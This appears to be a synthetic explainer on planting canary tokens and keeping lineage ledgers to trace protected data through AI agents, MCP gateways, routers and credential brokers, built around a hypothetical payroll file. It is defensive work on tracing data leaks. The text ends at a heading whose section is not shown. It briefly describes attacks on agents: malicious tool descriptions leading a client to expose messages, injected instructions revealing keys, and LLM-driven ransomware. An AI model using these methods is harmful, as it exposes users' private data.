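# Synthetic canary tokens for tracing protected information through AI tools, agents and brokers

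## What canary tokens, brokers and lineage are

A canary token is a fake item of data planted among real data. If the token later appears elsewhere, that shows the data travelled there. Security staff have used such tokens for more than twenty years, mainly against intruders and prying employees. The tokens can also trace data through AI agents, programs in which a language model decides what steps to take and what outside software to call. An agent may pass its owner's data to tools and models that other companies run, often through intermediaries.

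A hypothetical payroll office has a scanned file of salaries. A member of the company's security team adds a line to it for an employee who does not exist, with the number 7Q4M-90218-KD. The office then asks an agent to turn the file into a spreadsheet, and the agent sends it to a text-recognition tool through an intermediary that the company uses for all its tools. Three weeks later, a search finds the number on a server the company has no dealings with.

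The fake number is the *canary*. The intermediary is a *broker*, which is anything that passes requests or data between an agent and a tool, a model or another agent. Each transfer between parties or components is a *hop*. The file made at least three hops, from the payroll store to the agent, from the agent to the broker, and from the broker to the tool. A place where data ends up is a *sink*. The unrelated server, the tool's log and the finished spreadsheet are all sinks, and the canary could turn up in any of them. The owner's policy is the only reason that finding it on the server is alarming and finding it in the spreadsheet is not. The company permits the text-recognition tool to receive salary data, so that transfer is an *allowed flow*, but it never permitted a transfer to the server.

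*Lineage* is the record that connects data's source to where it ends up. For the fake number, it would show which file the number came from, which hops it passed through, and what the tool and the agent derived from it. The security team also needs a *ledger*, a protected record that links each canary to the data around it, the recipient, the time and the call that led to the transfer. Without the ledger, someone who finds 7Q4M-90218-KD on an unfamiliar server can't tell what it means. A *sighting* is any observation of a canary after it has been planted.

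This is a *lexical canary* because a scanner can find it by its exact characters. If the tool had returned a summary of the payroll, those characters might have been lost. A *semantic canary* can survive rewording because an investigator recognises it by its meaning, style or structure. A *live canary*, such as a working key to an empty account or a unique web address, triggers an alert when used, so nobody has to search for it.

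### How a tool call carries the data

Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting AI applications to outside software. Anthropic introduced it in November 2024. *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026), a guidance paper from the US National Security Agency (NSA), describes it as the de facto standard for communication among AI-driven services. Model Context Protocol's *Architecture overview* distinguishes hosts, clients and servers. The host is the AI application. It creates an internal client for each connection to a server, which is a program that offers tools.

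In the salary case, the client first sends a `tools/list` request. The server returns each tool's name, description and input schema. The language model chooses the text-recognition tool from this list. The client then sends a `tools/call` request with the tool's name and its arguments, which include the salary file and the canary in it. The server runs the tool and returns the recognised text, which the client passes to the model for the next step.

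So the canary leaves the company before the tool has returned anything. Shabista, Gupta and Raunak (2026), in *Shadow Data in Tool Calls*, studied only this outbound half, using a prototype smart-home agent. In preliminary tests, most of the agent's calls leaked personal or sensitive information in the request parameters. For example, an agent that requests the weather at its user's doctor's office gives a third party the office's coordinates. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) recommends that applications show the user a tool's inputs before each call, to prevent malicious or accidental leaks. That would not have helped the payroll office much, since a person who wanted the file read would have approved the call.

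The Model Context Protocol (2026) project released a version of MCP on 28 July 2026 that removed the opening handshake and the session identifier. Each request now carries its own protocol version, client identity and client capabilities. The method and the tool's name also travel in HTTP headers, which sit outside the body of a web request, so a broker can route and authorise a call without parsing the body. A broker that does this will forward a canary in the arguments without examining it. However, a server's developer may mark an argument for copying into a header, where any proxy on the route can read it, including any canary it contains. The maintainers warn developers not to do this with passwords, keys or personal data.

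### Kinds of broker

An MCP gateway sits between an organisation's agents and the tool servers they use. Without one, each agent has to track server addresses, manage separate credentials and adapt to every change a server's operator makes. In *GatewayBench*, Zheng, Chen and colleagues (2026) argue that this quickly becomes unsustainable for a large organisation. They tested seven gateways, including Amazon's AgentCore and the open-source LiteLLM, and sorted them into two designs. Flattened gateways give the agent the full list of tools at the start, while hierarchical gateways give it a few discovery tools for finding the ones it needs. This matters for tracing because some hierarchical gateways take a search query that describes the task. If the agent copies a line containing the canary from the salary file into its query, the canary reaches the gateway before the agent calls the text-recognition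 tool.

A gateway looks like a single server to the client, but each call becomes two, one from the client to the gateway and another from the gateway to the server behind it. The gateway in *Scalable LLM Agent Tool Access in the Cloud* (2026) checks the client's identity on the first call and logs in to the tool on the client's behalf for the second.

Model routers forward prompts to the companies that host language models, so that a developer can use several hosts through one connection. Anand and Chattaraj (2026), in *Diagnosing Tool-Selection Reasoning in LLM Agents with Canary Tools*, used the router LiteLLM to reach six models from three providers. Zheng and colleagues tested LiteLLM as an MCP gateway, so one product can be both a router and a gateway. A router doesn't appear in any tool call, so it is easy to overlook when tracing where the salary data went. But the recognised text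 has to go back to the model, and if another company hosts that model, the text passes through the router and on to the host, which adds two hops to the three above.

A credential broker keeps passwords and keys out of the agent's hands. Agents often hold these secrets directly, in local files or environment variables. *CapSeal* (Jin, Guo and Cheung, 2026) points out that an agent that can use a key can also reveal it, for instance after an attacker has slipped instructions into its prompt. In the CapSeal prototype, the agent asks for permission to perform one narrow action, such as a single type of request to a single address. The broker checks this against its policy and issues a temporary handle. The agent then submits the handle with its data, and the broker adds the key, which the agent never sees, carries out the action and records it in a log that shows any tampering. The broker gives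 the submitted data weaker protection. It checks that the request has the permitted size and shape, so a salary file that meets both conditions goes through with the fake employee still in it.

A coordinating agent divides a task and delegates the parts to other agents. It is probably the most likely of the four to alter the information it passes on, because it may restate the task for each recipient, and the rewording may remove a lexical canary. The NSA warns that one agent may accept another's output without checking it, and that context shared by several tasks can leak from one to another. A coordinating agent that handled payroll in the morning could therefore include the fake number in an unrelated job that afternoon, even though nobody asked it to send salary data anywhere.

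### Did the data move, by which route, and who was responsible?

These are the questions that the number on the server might help to answer, and they get harder in that order.

To establish that the data moved, the company needs the sighting and good reason to think the string could not have come from anywhere else. The string has to be long and random enough that nobody would produce it by accident, and the ledger has to show that the team planted it only in this file. Even then, the sighting proves only that one line moved. The company has to infer that the real salaries moved with it, though the inference is strong if the neighbouring lines of the file are also on the server.

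The route is harder to trace because the number doesn't record which systems handled it. The gateway, the tool, the router and the model's host all did, and any of them could have leaked it. The leak may also have occurred outside that path. The NSA warns that a client may share information freely among unrelated servers, and describes a demonstration in which researchers attached a malicious server to an agent that already used a trusted WhatsApp tool. The malicious server's tool descriptions led the client to expose the user's messages. Another tool on the payroll agent could have obtained the fake number the same way.

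One remedy is to give each recipient a different canary. In an article hosted by Symantec (2003), the security specialist Lance Spitzner described planting a different false login in each vice-president's email, so that the login an intruder tries shows whose mail they read. The payroll office could likewise put a different fake employee in each tool's copy. If one of these fake employees turned up in a leak, the office would know which tool's copy it came from, but not whether the tool or the gateway in front of it was responsible, because both handled the same copy.

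For that, the company needs records from each hop, and these are often poor. According to the NSA, many MCP implementations keep no logs or only minimal operational data. Where logs exist, they may identify the wrong party. *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile* (2026) explains that the databases and other systems behind an MCP server check only the server's identity and have no information about the agent that began the call. A database's log would therefore name the server, whichever agent made the request.

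If the records do show that the number left from the text-recognition tool, the tool's operator may have sold the file or suffered a break-in. It may also have stored the file with a subcontractor that the contract permits, in which case the flow was allowed and the company did not recognise the server. Responsibility depends on intent, control and what the parties agreed, and the number is not evidence of any of these. Spitzner made the same point in the Symantec article. An employee who copies a planted document may be stealing it or may be confused, and the employer needs other means to find out which.

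Investigating a broker is also difficult because the broker often keeps the records. A tamper-evident log such as the one in CapSeal helps against later alteration, but Jin and colleagues assume that the broker is trustworthy, which an investigator who suspects the broker cannot do.

### Where the idea comes from

The practice is older than the name *honeytoken*. In the 2003 article, Spitzner mentions map-makers who added bogus towns and roads to expose copyists, and Cliff Stoll's book *The Cuckoo's Egg*, in which he plants files to track a German hacker. Augusto Paes de Barros proposed the name in February 2003 for information that should not be moving across a network, so detecting it there means something is wrong. The honeytoken extended the idea of the honeypot, a decoy computer with no legitimate users.

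Spitzner (2003), in *Protocol Anomaly Detection IDS*, answered on 21 February with an example close to the salary case: a document titled "payroll" with a tracking number, 14A8478bG98734T90AAZ, that detection software could search for. In April, Spitzner (2003), in *Honeytokens and detection*, extended the idea to false numbers in databases, after reports that thefts of card and social security numbers had gone unnoticed, sometimes for months. The later article credits Paes de Barros with coining the term but says he did so on a honeypots mailing list. The archives show that the exchange took place on an intrusion detection list and that Spitzner (2003), in *HoneyTokens*, forwarded it to the honeypots list the same day.

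Official guidance followed in 2020 with the fifth revision of SP 800-53, *Security and Privacy Controls for Information Systems and Organizations*, from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST). Open Security Architecture's *SI-20 Tainting* lists the relevant control, SI-20, as new in that revision. Under SI-20, organisations "embed data or capabilities" in chosen systems to find out whether anyone has exfiltrated or improperly removed their data. NIST's examples range from passive to active. An organisation can add false email addresses to an internal database and watch for mail sent to them. It can hide data in files so that a search of public sources will find them. Or it can embed software that calls home, which reveals the capture and possibly the location and the path by which the data left. NIST's August 2025 amendments do not change SI-20.

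Spitzner's honeytoken has no authorised use, so any contact with it is suspicious. But the canary in the salary file is a fake employee that travels inside a real file along an allowed flow, and the gateway and the tool are supposed to handle it. An alarm on every contact would go off at every legitimate call, so the company has to judge each sighting by where it occurs.

### Other things called canaries

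In research on model training, a canary is a sequence that testers insert into the training data to measure what the model memorises. *Advancing the State-of-the-Art in Empirical Privacy Auditing* (Mitchell, Andrew and colleagues, 2026) traces this use to work by Carlini and colleagues in 2019. Anand and Chattaraj use "canary tools" to mean flawed tools placed among an agent's real ones. Each flawed tool exposes a particular weakness in how the agent chooses, such as a preference for whatever sounds most powerful. Unlike a watermark, which is a pattern that its maker adds to genuine content to show where the content came from, a canary is a separate, false item placed beside genuine data.

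Canary tokens for tracing are most closely related to decoys that catch an agent exceeding its permissions, which are often called canary tokens too. Thinkst's *One for all the models out there!* introduces such a decoy, a fake MCP configuration file that alerts its owner when an agent connects to the server listed in the file or calls one of that server's tools. This kind of decoy stays where its owner put it, while a canary for tracing has to travel with the data.

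## Designing and planting the canaries

A canary found on an unfamiliar server indicates a leak only if the server's owner had no right to the data. The payroll office therefore has to decide who has that right before it plants any canaries. If it waits until one turns up, it will have to decide when somebody may be to blame.

### Mapping the allowed flows

An allowed-flow map lists each recipient, what it may receive and what it may keep. The office's map might begin like this:

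| Recipient | May receive | May keep |
|---|---|---|
| MCP gateway | The whole file, in transit | Tool names and call times, but no arguments |
| Text-recognition tool | The whole file | A copy for 30 days, on its own servers or its named subcontractor's |
| Model router | The recognised text, in transit | Nothing |
| Model's host | The recognised text | A copy for 30 days, for abuse checks |
| Payroll staff | The finished spreadsheet | The spreadsheet, for as long as the law requires |

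The gateway is allowed to transmit the fake employee's number but not to store it, so finding the number in the gateway's debugging log shows that it retained data improperly. The map also has to name the subcontractor, or the number's presence on the subcontractor's server will look like theft.

NIST's control on boundary protection, SC-7, can serve as a model for keeping such a map. Under its enhancements, organisations refuse network traffic they have not approved, write a traffic flow policy for each managed interface to an outside telecommunications service, and record the business need for each exception and its duration. For systems that handle personal information, they also monitor external interfaces and key internal boundaries to check that the processing is permitted. The durations are easy to neglect. If the office tries out another text-recognition tool in May and ends the trial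 in June, a canary that reaches the tool in July is a leak, although the same transfer was permitted in May.

### Choosing a form

A random string is easy to search for and unlikely to appear by chance. *ContextLeak* (Choi, Cao and colleagues, 2025) compared random hexadecimal strings, rare words and false statements, such as that the sun rises in the west. The researchers placed a canary among the examples in a model's prompt in about half of the runs, then tried to tell from the model's answers whether it was there. The hexadecimal strings did consistently well on most of the models, and the researchers recommend starting with them. But they wrote their queries to draw the canary out. A dishonest broker would want to remove the canary, and a random string is the easiest kind to remove. *Who Owns This Agent?* (2026), a paper on tracing AI agents to their owners, includes instructions for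 a language model to filter web pages by removing or replacing hexadecimal strings and similar codes.

A plausible record, such as the fake employee, is harder to filter out because it resembles the data around it. *WiP* (2024), a work-in-progress paper on layered deception, describes an experiment by Shabtai and colleagues in which students played bankers who approved loans for a commission but could earn more by improperly referring customers to a private lender. When fake requests made up 20% of the loan list, the researchers detected all of the loans that the students referred. However, they had made the fake loans lucrative enough to tempt dishonest players. A tracing canary offers no such incentive and works only if the recipient copies it along with everything else.

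Plausibility depends on local detail. *PHANTOM* (Weinberg, 2026) generated 32 fake credentials from the names, services and conventions of four sample organisations, and 32 more from generic templates. The two sets scored about the same for correct format, but the tailored ones scored 0.705 for fit with the organisation, against 0.396 for the templates. The paper also reports that "human acceptance" rose from 6% to 100%, but a program awarded the scores, not people, and it gave credit for the same organisation-specific terms that PHANTOM inserts. It also checked Amazon key identifiers against a length of 21 characters, when real ones have 20. The work is more useful as a guide to what gives a template away, such as `example.com` or `changeme`. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* (Chauhan and Revankar, 2026) adds prefixes, checksums, lengths and unusual randomness to the list.

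A live canary helps when the data may go somewhere the office cannot search. Thinkst's *A "Safety Net" for AWS Canarytokens* (2022) describes keys to AWS, Amazon's cloud service, that reveal the caller's IP address and the operation the caller attempted. Thieves may try such keys almost at once. *Somebody Is Hunting For Your AI API Keys With A Fake GrokBot* (2026), by the security blogger hrbrmstr, reports that six cloud machines stole 53 canary AWS keys from a group of decoy servers over six days and tried to use them on Amazon's AI service within ten seconds of each theft. The alert can take much longer, because Amazon's logging may delay it by 2 to 30 minutes, according to Thinkst's *How do I create an AWS API Key Canarytoken*.

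However, a live canary raises an alarm only when someone uses it. A broker that stores a fake key and never tries it goes undetected, and *WiP* notes that a document with a hidden beacon may stay silent if the thief reads it offline. A careful thief may also recognise the canary. Grafana Labs' *Canary tokens* describes an intruder who triggered the company's canary by running the stolen secrets through TruffleHog, a scanner that tests whether keys work. TruffleHog recognises the free versions of these canaries without trying them, so the company would have missed the intruder if it had planted those. AWS also limits the number of keys. Tracebit's *Deploying effective canary AWS credentials* puts the limit at 10,000 long-term keys per account, so two million would need 200 accounts.

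A marked document carries a hidden identifier in its own text. This suits contracts, reports and other prose, which have no rows where a fake employee could be hidden. For the salary file, a fake employee works better, with a random-looking staff number to make the entry unique.

### Deriving the token from a secret key

The team could draw each staff number at random and record it in the ledger. A keyed hash, or HMAC, does better because the team can later prove that the number is one of its own. An HMAC takes a secret key and a message and returns a string of fixed length. Anyone with both can recompute the string, but without the key nobody can feasibly work out the right string for a new message. For the salary file, the message would contain the record, the recipient and the time:

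`token = first 16 bytes of HMAC-SHA256(key, record | recipient | time)`

Including the recipient in the message gives each recipient's copy its own token, but the team has to mark where each field ends. Otherwise, record 12 for recipient 3 and record 1 for recipient 23 would both give the message "123", and so the same token.

To check a sighting, the team looks up the string in the ledger and recomputes the HMAC from the record, recipient and time listed there. If the result matches, someone with the key made the string, so an outsider who invented a number and claimed to have found it would fail the check. An outsider who copied a real canary from a file would pass, wherever they claimed to have found it. Readers must also take the team's word for the time, since a member with the key could compute a backdated token.

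Raz, Putrevu and colleagues (2026), in *Safeguarding LLMs Against Misuse and AI-Driven Malware Using Steganographic Canaries*, derive their tokens in nearly the same way, from an organisation's key and a file's identifier, but also offer a digital signature as an alternative to the HMAC. With an HMAC, an outside company that checks for canaries needs either the secret key, which would also let it forge tokens, or a current list of valid tokens. With a signature, it needs only a 32-byte public key, which can verify tokens but not create them. Signed tokens are larger, taking up 70 bytes for the identifier, signature and length field, compared with 18 for the HMAC version.

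### How long the token has to be

If two canaries are identical, a sighting could come from either planting. The expected number of collisions is the number of pairs divided by the number of possible values. Two million canaries form 2,000,000 × 1,999,999 ÷ 2 pairs, or about 2 × 10¹². Six characters from a 36-symbol alphabet allow 36⁶ values, or 2,176,782,336, so about 919 pairs should collide. The table compares this with other formats, assuming every value is equally likely, which is very nearly true with an HMAC.

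| Format | Possible values | Expected colliding pairs | Chance that a stranger's random string matches a canary |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nine digits | 1.0 × 10⁹ | 2,000 | 1 in 500 |
| Six letters or digits | 2.2 × 10⁹ | 919 | 1 in 1,088 |
| The pattern of 7Q4M-90218-KD | 1.1 × 10¹⁴ | 0.02 | 1 in 57 million |
| 128 random bits | 3.4 × 10³⁸ | 6 × 10⁻²⁷ | 1 in 1.7 × 10³² |

The team can prevent collisions among its own canaries by having the ledger reject duplicates, but it can't control the strings other people generate, so the last column matters more. A log containing a million random six-character codes would produce about 919 false sightings.

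The same calculation also shows a weakness in the signature scheme. Raz and colleagues shorten each file's identifier to four bytes before signing it, which leaves about 4.3 billion possible values. A collision is unlikely with the 10,000 files per organisation that they assume, but two million files would produce about 466 colliding pairs. The two files in each pair would have the same signature, despite its length, because this type of signature is always the same for the same input.

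### Long and random, or short and believable

A 128-bit canary takes 32 hexadecimal characters, which would look out of place as a staff number in a payroll system. A surname or a town looks realistic, but finding one in a tool's output doesn't show that it came from the planted record.

*Identifying AI Web Scrapers Using Canary Tokens* (Seiden, Kim and colleagues, 2026) describes this problem in live chatbots. The researchers built 20 websites about invented people and companies, showed each visiting scraper different names, towns and figures, and then looked for these details in the chatbots' answers. In the first round they found 2,325 tokens and had to discard 928 of them, or 40%. Of these, 618 were numbers, which a chatbot might produce for unrelated reasons, such as giving 2024 as the end of its training data. Chatbots also rounded some figures. Another 207 were values that the sites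 had used more than once, and 102 were parts of longer tokens, such as "Port" from "West Port". The researchers discarded every numerical match as a precaution, so not all 928 were errors, but they had no automatic way to tell which were genuine.

The smallest set of values they drew from had 4,761 entries, and an average site had 592 distinct visitors. If the draws were independent, the sum above gives about 37 colliding pairs for that one field on an average site, which may explain some of the 207, although the paper calls the chance of a collision small.

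They addressed this by requiring at least two tokens before linking a scraper to a chatbot. The payroll office can apply the same idea to a whole record. Four fields with 4,761 possible values each allow about 5 × 10¹⁴ combinations, which reduces the expected number of collisions among two million canaries to 0.004. The team can derive the values from the HMAC, using some of its bits for the surname and others for the town, job title and starting date. The record is then believable, and the team can still verify it, but all four fields have to survive together, whereas a single long number is enough by itself.

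### Where to plant them

The canary must be where a recipient will copy it along with the real data. File properties, comments and hidden fields are poor places for it because software drops them when it extracts the text. The top and bottom of a file are also risky, since an agent may cut a title row or send only the first few pages. Seiden and colleagues spread ten tokens through each web page in case a chatbot's software stripped or truncated the page. In the salary file, the fake employees should be listed among the real ones, with at least one in each department or office that someone might extract separately. Their salaries and starting dates should be unremarkable, so that a filter, such as one for staff earning less than £60,000, doesn't remove them all.

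Because the salary file is a scan, the canary has to be visible on the page for the tool to read it, and the tool may mistake a zero for the letter O. A fixed pattern such as 7Q4M-90218-KD helps because the team knows that the middle five characters are digits and can correct for the error when it searches.

The number of canaries to plant depends on how much of the file might leak. If the whole file leaks, one is enough. If a thousand-row file contains ten fake employees and a random hundred rows leak, the chance that they include at least one canary is about 65%. The team would need 28 fake employees to raise it to 95%.

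With credentials, a thief may take only one. Chauhan and Revankar model a thief who picks at random among *m* real credentials and *k* canaries:

`chance of detection = k / (m + k) × (1 − β)`

Here β is the chance that the detector misses a canary that has leaked. The paper's detector missed 1% in a small test. At that rate, one real key among four canaries would give a detection chance of about 79%. The formula fails if anything shows which key is real, such as a label or a tool that visibly uses it.

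### Keeping them harmless

The fake employee must not match a real person. Seiden and colleagues searched the internet to check that their invented people did not resemble real ones, and they also made up the telephone numbers and universities. An invented number in a valid format may still belong to somebody, so it is safer to use numbers that are never assigned to anyone, such as the US telephone numbers from 555-0100 to 555-0199, which the numbering authorities reserve for fiction.

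A live canary key must not grant access to anything. *Breach Detection at Scale with AWS Honey Tokens* (Bourke and Grzelak, 2018) describes SPACECRAB, a tool that gives every key a policy denying all actions on all resources. A thief who tries the key gets an error, and the record of the failed attempt triggers an alert. The tool also stores where the team planted each key and who has to respond if someone uses it. Thinkst goes further by hosting the infrastructure itself, so its keys have no connection to anything the customer owns.

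The canaries also must not interfere with legitimate work. If an agent finds a fake key beside the real one, it may try the fake one, fail at its task and raise a false alarm. Chauhan and Revankar avoid this by storing the real credentials in a separate list that the tool software reads, and putting canaries only in the text the model sees.

In the payroll office, the equivalent mistake would be to pay the fake employee. Ten fake employees in a staff of a thousand would also add 1% to the headcount and distort the salary bill and any average based on it. The office should keep a list of them with the ledger and remove them when the spreadsheet comes back, before anyone runs the payroll or compiles statistics. It should not mark them in a "test record" column, because the column would travel with the file and give the canaries away. The few people who run the payroll need to know that the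 list exists, or one of them will eventually spend time trying to identify the extra employee.

Each canary needs an expiry date, after which the team removes it from the live data and plants a new one. Raz and colleagues give two weeks as an example. Grafana Labs advises replacing a canary as soon as it triggers and keeping the old one for the investigation. The team should keep the ledger entry and the key behind it for years after removing the canary, because copies of the salary file that have already got out will still contain it.

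### A framework for marked documents

In March 2026, Raz and colleagues published the most thorough test of marked documents for AI services. They were concerned about malware that sends stolen files to a hosted language model for analysis, and about employees who paste confidential papers into a chatbot. In both cases the text has to enter the AI service, so they put the check at that point. They used steganography, which hides information inside something that looks ordinary.

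Mode A marks real documents. It hides the whole 18-byte payload, which consists of the HMAC token and its length, in three separate ways:

- **Whitespace:** it replaces ordinary spaces with one of four similar-looking Unicode spaces. Each replacement carries two bits, so the payload takes 72 spaces.
- **Zero-width characters:** it inserts 72 invisible characters between the visible ones, spread through the document.
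- **Lookalike letters:** it replaces Latin letters with Cyrillic ones of the same shape, such as the Cyrillic "а". Each suitable letter carries one bit, so the payload takes 144 of them.

Mode B creates synthetic documents with GPT-2, a small language model from 2019. The program treats the payload as a number between 0 and 1. At each step, GPT-2 assigns a probability to every next token (a word or part of a word), and the program divides the current range among the tokens in proportion to their probabilities. It picks the token whose share contains the number, then repeats within that share. A decoder with the same model and settings can retrace the choices and recover the payload. Mode B then adds zero-width characters and lookalike letters.

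The check runs in a proxy between the user and the model. For each request, the proxy extracts any hidden characters and looks up the result in the list of valid tokens, then strips the marks and tries to decode the wording itself. If any layer produces a verified match, the proxy refuses that request and all later ones. Mode A's three checks add less than a millisecond in total, and Mode B's add about 0.2 seconds.

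The researchers put 100 documents per method through twelve conversions to find out what destroys the marks. The documents marked with hidden characters were Wikipedia extracts of about 3,000 characters, and those marked through their wording were GPT-2 output. The table gives the share of documents from which the researchers recovered the token.

| Conversion | Whitespace | Zero-width | Lookalikes | GPT-2 wording |
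|---|---|---|---|---|
| Copy and paste, new line breaks, curly quotes or trimmed line ends | 100% | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| Unicode normalisation (NFKC), which standardises variant characters | 0% | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| Collapsing whitespace | 0% | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| Removing invisible characters | 100% | 0% | 100% | 100% |
| Turning lookalikes back into Latin letters | 100% | 100% | 0% | 100% |
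| Removing everything outside basic ASCII | 0% | 0% | 0% | 98% |
| Removing punctuation and capitals | 100% | 100% | 8% | 0% |
| Paraphrase by a language model | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |

Mixing methods helped, but extra copies of the same mark would not have, because in any one document a conversion either left a mark readable or ruined it completely. Mode A survived ordinary clean-up in every document because of the lookalike letters, but it did not survive an attacker who stripped all three kinds of character. Mode B survived clean-up in 99% of documents and the attacker in 97%. The abstract overstates the results by claiming 100% recovery for all methods under ordinary clean-up, since the whitespace and zero-width marks each failed there when used alone.

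Adding the whitespace marks to Mode B reduced recovery after the attack from 97% to zero. Removing the unusual spaces ran words together, so the GPT-2 decoder could no longer track its position in the text.

To test for false alarms, the researchers ran four decoders on 100 unmarked documents, with both HMACs and signatures, and none of the 800 attempts produced a verified match. Marking a file took under a millisecond in Mode A. In Mode B it took about 1.4 seconds with an HMAC and 4 seconds with a signature, so marking 10,000 documents would take about 4 or 11 hours, respectively, on the researchers' graphics card.

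Another test ran the system against ransomware that uses a language model to choose which files to attack. The ransomware ran on a virtual machine with 288 files, two of them canaries. Without the check, it took 177 seconds to encrypt its targets and write a ransom note. With the check on, the proxy caught a Mode A canary after 63 seconds and a Mode B canary after 113, both before any encryption. Each result comes from a single run. The Mode B files had names meant to attract a thief, such as `Crypto_Wallet_Seed_Phrase.txt`, and the malware sent their text unaltered.

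The payroll office could run the same check at its gateway, but the response would have to depend on the recipient. The proxy in the study blocks every canary it finds, whereas the office's map allows the salary file to go to the text-recognition tool. The check also has no effect on a thief who uses a model on their own machine or one hosted by a company that doesn't run the check.

Mode A is a poor fit for the salary file because a surname with a Cyrillic letter in it looks correct but no longer matches the same surname in the payroll system. Text recognition would probably erase all three marks, because the software recognizes shapes and outputs standard characters. The researchers did not test text recognition or excerpts. The whitespace and lookalike marks start at the top of a document and stop once the payload is complete, so a tool that received only the last page of a long report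 might receive no mark.

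## Recording lineage from one call to the next

A fake employee's number on an unfamiliar server shows where the data came from and where it ended up, but not how it got there. To trace the route, the payroll office can change the number as the file moves, record every transfer, or do both.

### One token or a new one at each hop

Keeping one token throughout takes little work because the team plants it once, makes one ledger entry, and nobody has to edit the file again. A copy that leaks from any point is still recognisable as the salary file. But every party that handled the file had the same token, so finding it in a leaked copy doesn't narrow down where the leak happened.

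The alternative is to use a fresh token for each transfer. Suppose every transfer passes through a gateway that the company runs. Before passing the file on, the gateway replaces the old fake employee with a new one, whose number is derived from the team's secret key. Because the recipient's copy then has a different number from the sender's, a leaked number identifies the transfer that produced that copy.

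Replacing the number at each transfer is harder than it first appears. The gateway can replace it only in transfers it handles, so if a tool's operator sends the file to a subcontractor, both hold the same number. Each replacement also alters the file, which invalidates any digital signature on it, and if the file is a scan, the gateway has to edit an image. A thousand files with five transfers each need 5,000 tokens instead of 1,000, and the office has to recognise whichever number comes back to remove the fake employee before running the payroll.

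If each hop added a token and left the old ones in place, the file would carry a history of its route. But a recipient could delete the newest token before leaking the file, and the leak would appear to come from an earlier recipient.

The office can combine the two methods by planting a fixed fake employee in each part of the file and adding one more whose number changes at every transfer. The fixed employees show which part leaked, and the changing number shows which transfer the leaked copy came from.

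### What goes in the ledger

The gateway writes one row for each transfer:

| Field | Contents |
|---|---|
| Token | The number of the fake employee inserted for this transfer |
| Source item | An identifier for the data sent, such as "June salaries, Leeds pages" |
| Sender | The party or component that supplied the data |
| Recipient | The party or component that received it |
| Parent call | The earlier call or calls from which the sender got the data |
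| Time | When the gateway passed the data on, by its own clock |
| Policy decision | Whether the policy allowed the transfer, and which version of the policy applied |

Recording the parent call for each transfer links the transfers into a lineage. The parent field has to accept more than one value, since a call that combines two files has two parents. The ledger should record the source item as an identifier or a hash (a short fingerprint computed from the data), because storing the salaries themselves would create another copy of the payroll to protect.

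The gateway should write the row before it releases the data. If it crashes in between, the ledger will contain a transfer that never happened, which is a much smaller problem than a transfer with no row. The gateway should also record the calls it refuses, because an agent that tried three times to send the salary file to an unapproved address is worth knowing about even though no data got out.

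### Three hops with a split and a merge

Suppose the salary file covers two offices. The payroll store sends the London pages to one agent and the Leeds pages to another. Each agent extracts the text and sends it to a spreadsheet tool, which combines the two parts, and the finished spreadsheet goes to a pensions adviser. Every route from the file to the adviser has three hops. The numbers in brackets are calls:

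```
               +-(1)-> London agent -(3)-+
               |                         |
salary file ---+                         +-> spreadsheet -(5)-> pensions
               |                         |      tool            adviser
               +-(2)-> Leeds agent --(4)-+
```

The London pages contain the fixed fake employee 7Q4M-90218-KD and the Leeds pages contain 2B9X-64035-TW. The gateway adds a changing one to each transfer and records these rows:

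| Call | Token | Source item | Sender | Recipient | Parent call | Time | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 3H8T-55107-LM | London pages | Payroll store | London agent | None | 10:02 | Allow |
| 2 | 9C2R-13846-PX | Leeds pages | Payroll store | Leeds agent | None | 10:02 | Allow |
| 3 | 5V6N-70932-QF | London text | London agent | Spreadsheet tool | 1 | 10:04 | Allow |
| 4 | 8J1W-26479-BD | Leeds text | Leeds agent | Spreadsheet tool | 2 | 10:05 | Allow |
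| 5 | 6D3K-41820-GS | Spreadsheet | Spreadsheet tool | Pensions adviser | 3, 4 | 10:09 | Allow |

A month later, a search finds 6D3K-41820-GS on an unfamiliar server. The team looks up the number, finds call 5, and recomputes the keyed hash to confirm that the number is genuine. The parents of call 5 are calls 3 and 4, whose parents are calls 1 and 2. Calls 1 and 2 have no parents, so the trace ends at the London and Leeds pages of the salary file.

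The number also rules out most of the copies. The two agents held copies with other numbers, and so did the spreadsheet tool, because the gateway inserted 6D3K-41820-GS after the tool had handed over the spreadsheet. The leaked copy is therefore the one sent to the adviser, unless the gateway itself leaked it, but this does not establish whether the adviser is to blame.

If the server also holds the fixed Leeds employee but not the London one, the leaked rows probably came from Leeds, by way of calls 2 and 4. If the search had instead found 9C2R-13846-PX, the leak would have come from the Leeds agent's copy, before the merge. A ledger that recorded only one parent per call would have lost half of this graph at call 5.

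### What trace identifiers add

To find faults, many companies already follow requests from one service to the next. The World Wide Web Consortium (W3C), which sets web standards, has a Recommendation called Trace Context that defines how services pass on the identifiers needed for this. *Trace Context Level 3*, a draft of a newer version, specifies a 16-byte `trace-id` for the whole trace and an 8-byte `parent-id` for the step that sent the request.

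MCP messages carry these identifiers in `_meta`, a field for information about the message. A Model Context Protocol proposal reserves three names in it: `traceparent` for the identifiers, `tracestate` for data belonging to particular tracing products, and `baggage` for values that developers choose. A call might look like this:

```json
{
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "make_spreadsheet",
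    "arguments": { "text": "..." },
    "_meta": {
      "traceparent": "00-4bf92f3577b34da6a3ce929d0e0e4736-a91c07e25bd3f648-01"
    }
  }
}
```

According to Model Context Protocol's *Server Context*, the official Ruby software kit leaves all three values unchanged in incoming requests. The sender has to supply them. Langfuse, which makes monitoring software, notes in its documentation that an MCP client and server produce separate traces by default and that developers can link them by passing the trace context along.

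If the ledger stores the `trace-id` beside each call, the office can match its rows with the tool operator's logs, even when the clocks disagree and the operator never logged the data itself. This makes the right entries much quicker to find.

But a trace follows a request, and the request may not contain the data. If the Leeds agent looks up an exchange rate while working on the salaries, the exchange-rate service will log the same `trace-id` even though it received no salary data. A trace is just as likely to miss data that did move. If the pensions adviser saves the spreadsheet and emails it to someone a week later, the email belongs to another trace or to none. The format also allows only one `parent-id`, so it can't represent the merge at call 5. And because the identifiers are unsigned, any service on the route can drop them or attach them to an unrelated request.

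Putting the canary in `baggage` would defeat its purpose, because the canary could then reach the exchange-rate service without the file.

### Why agents should not report their own lineage

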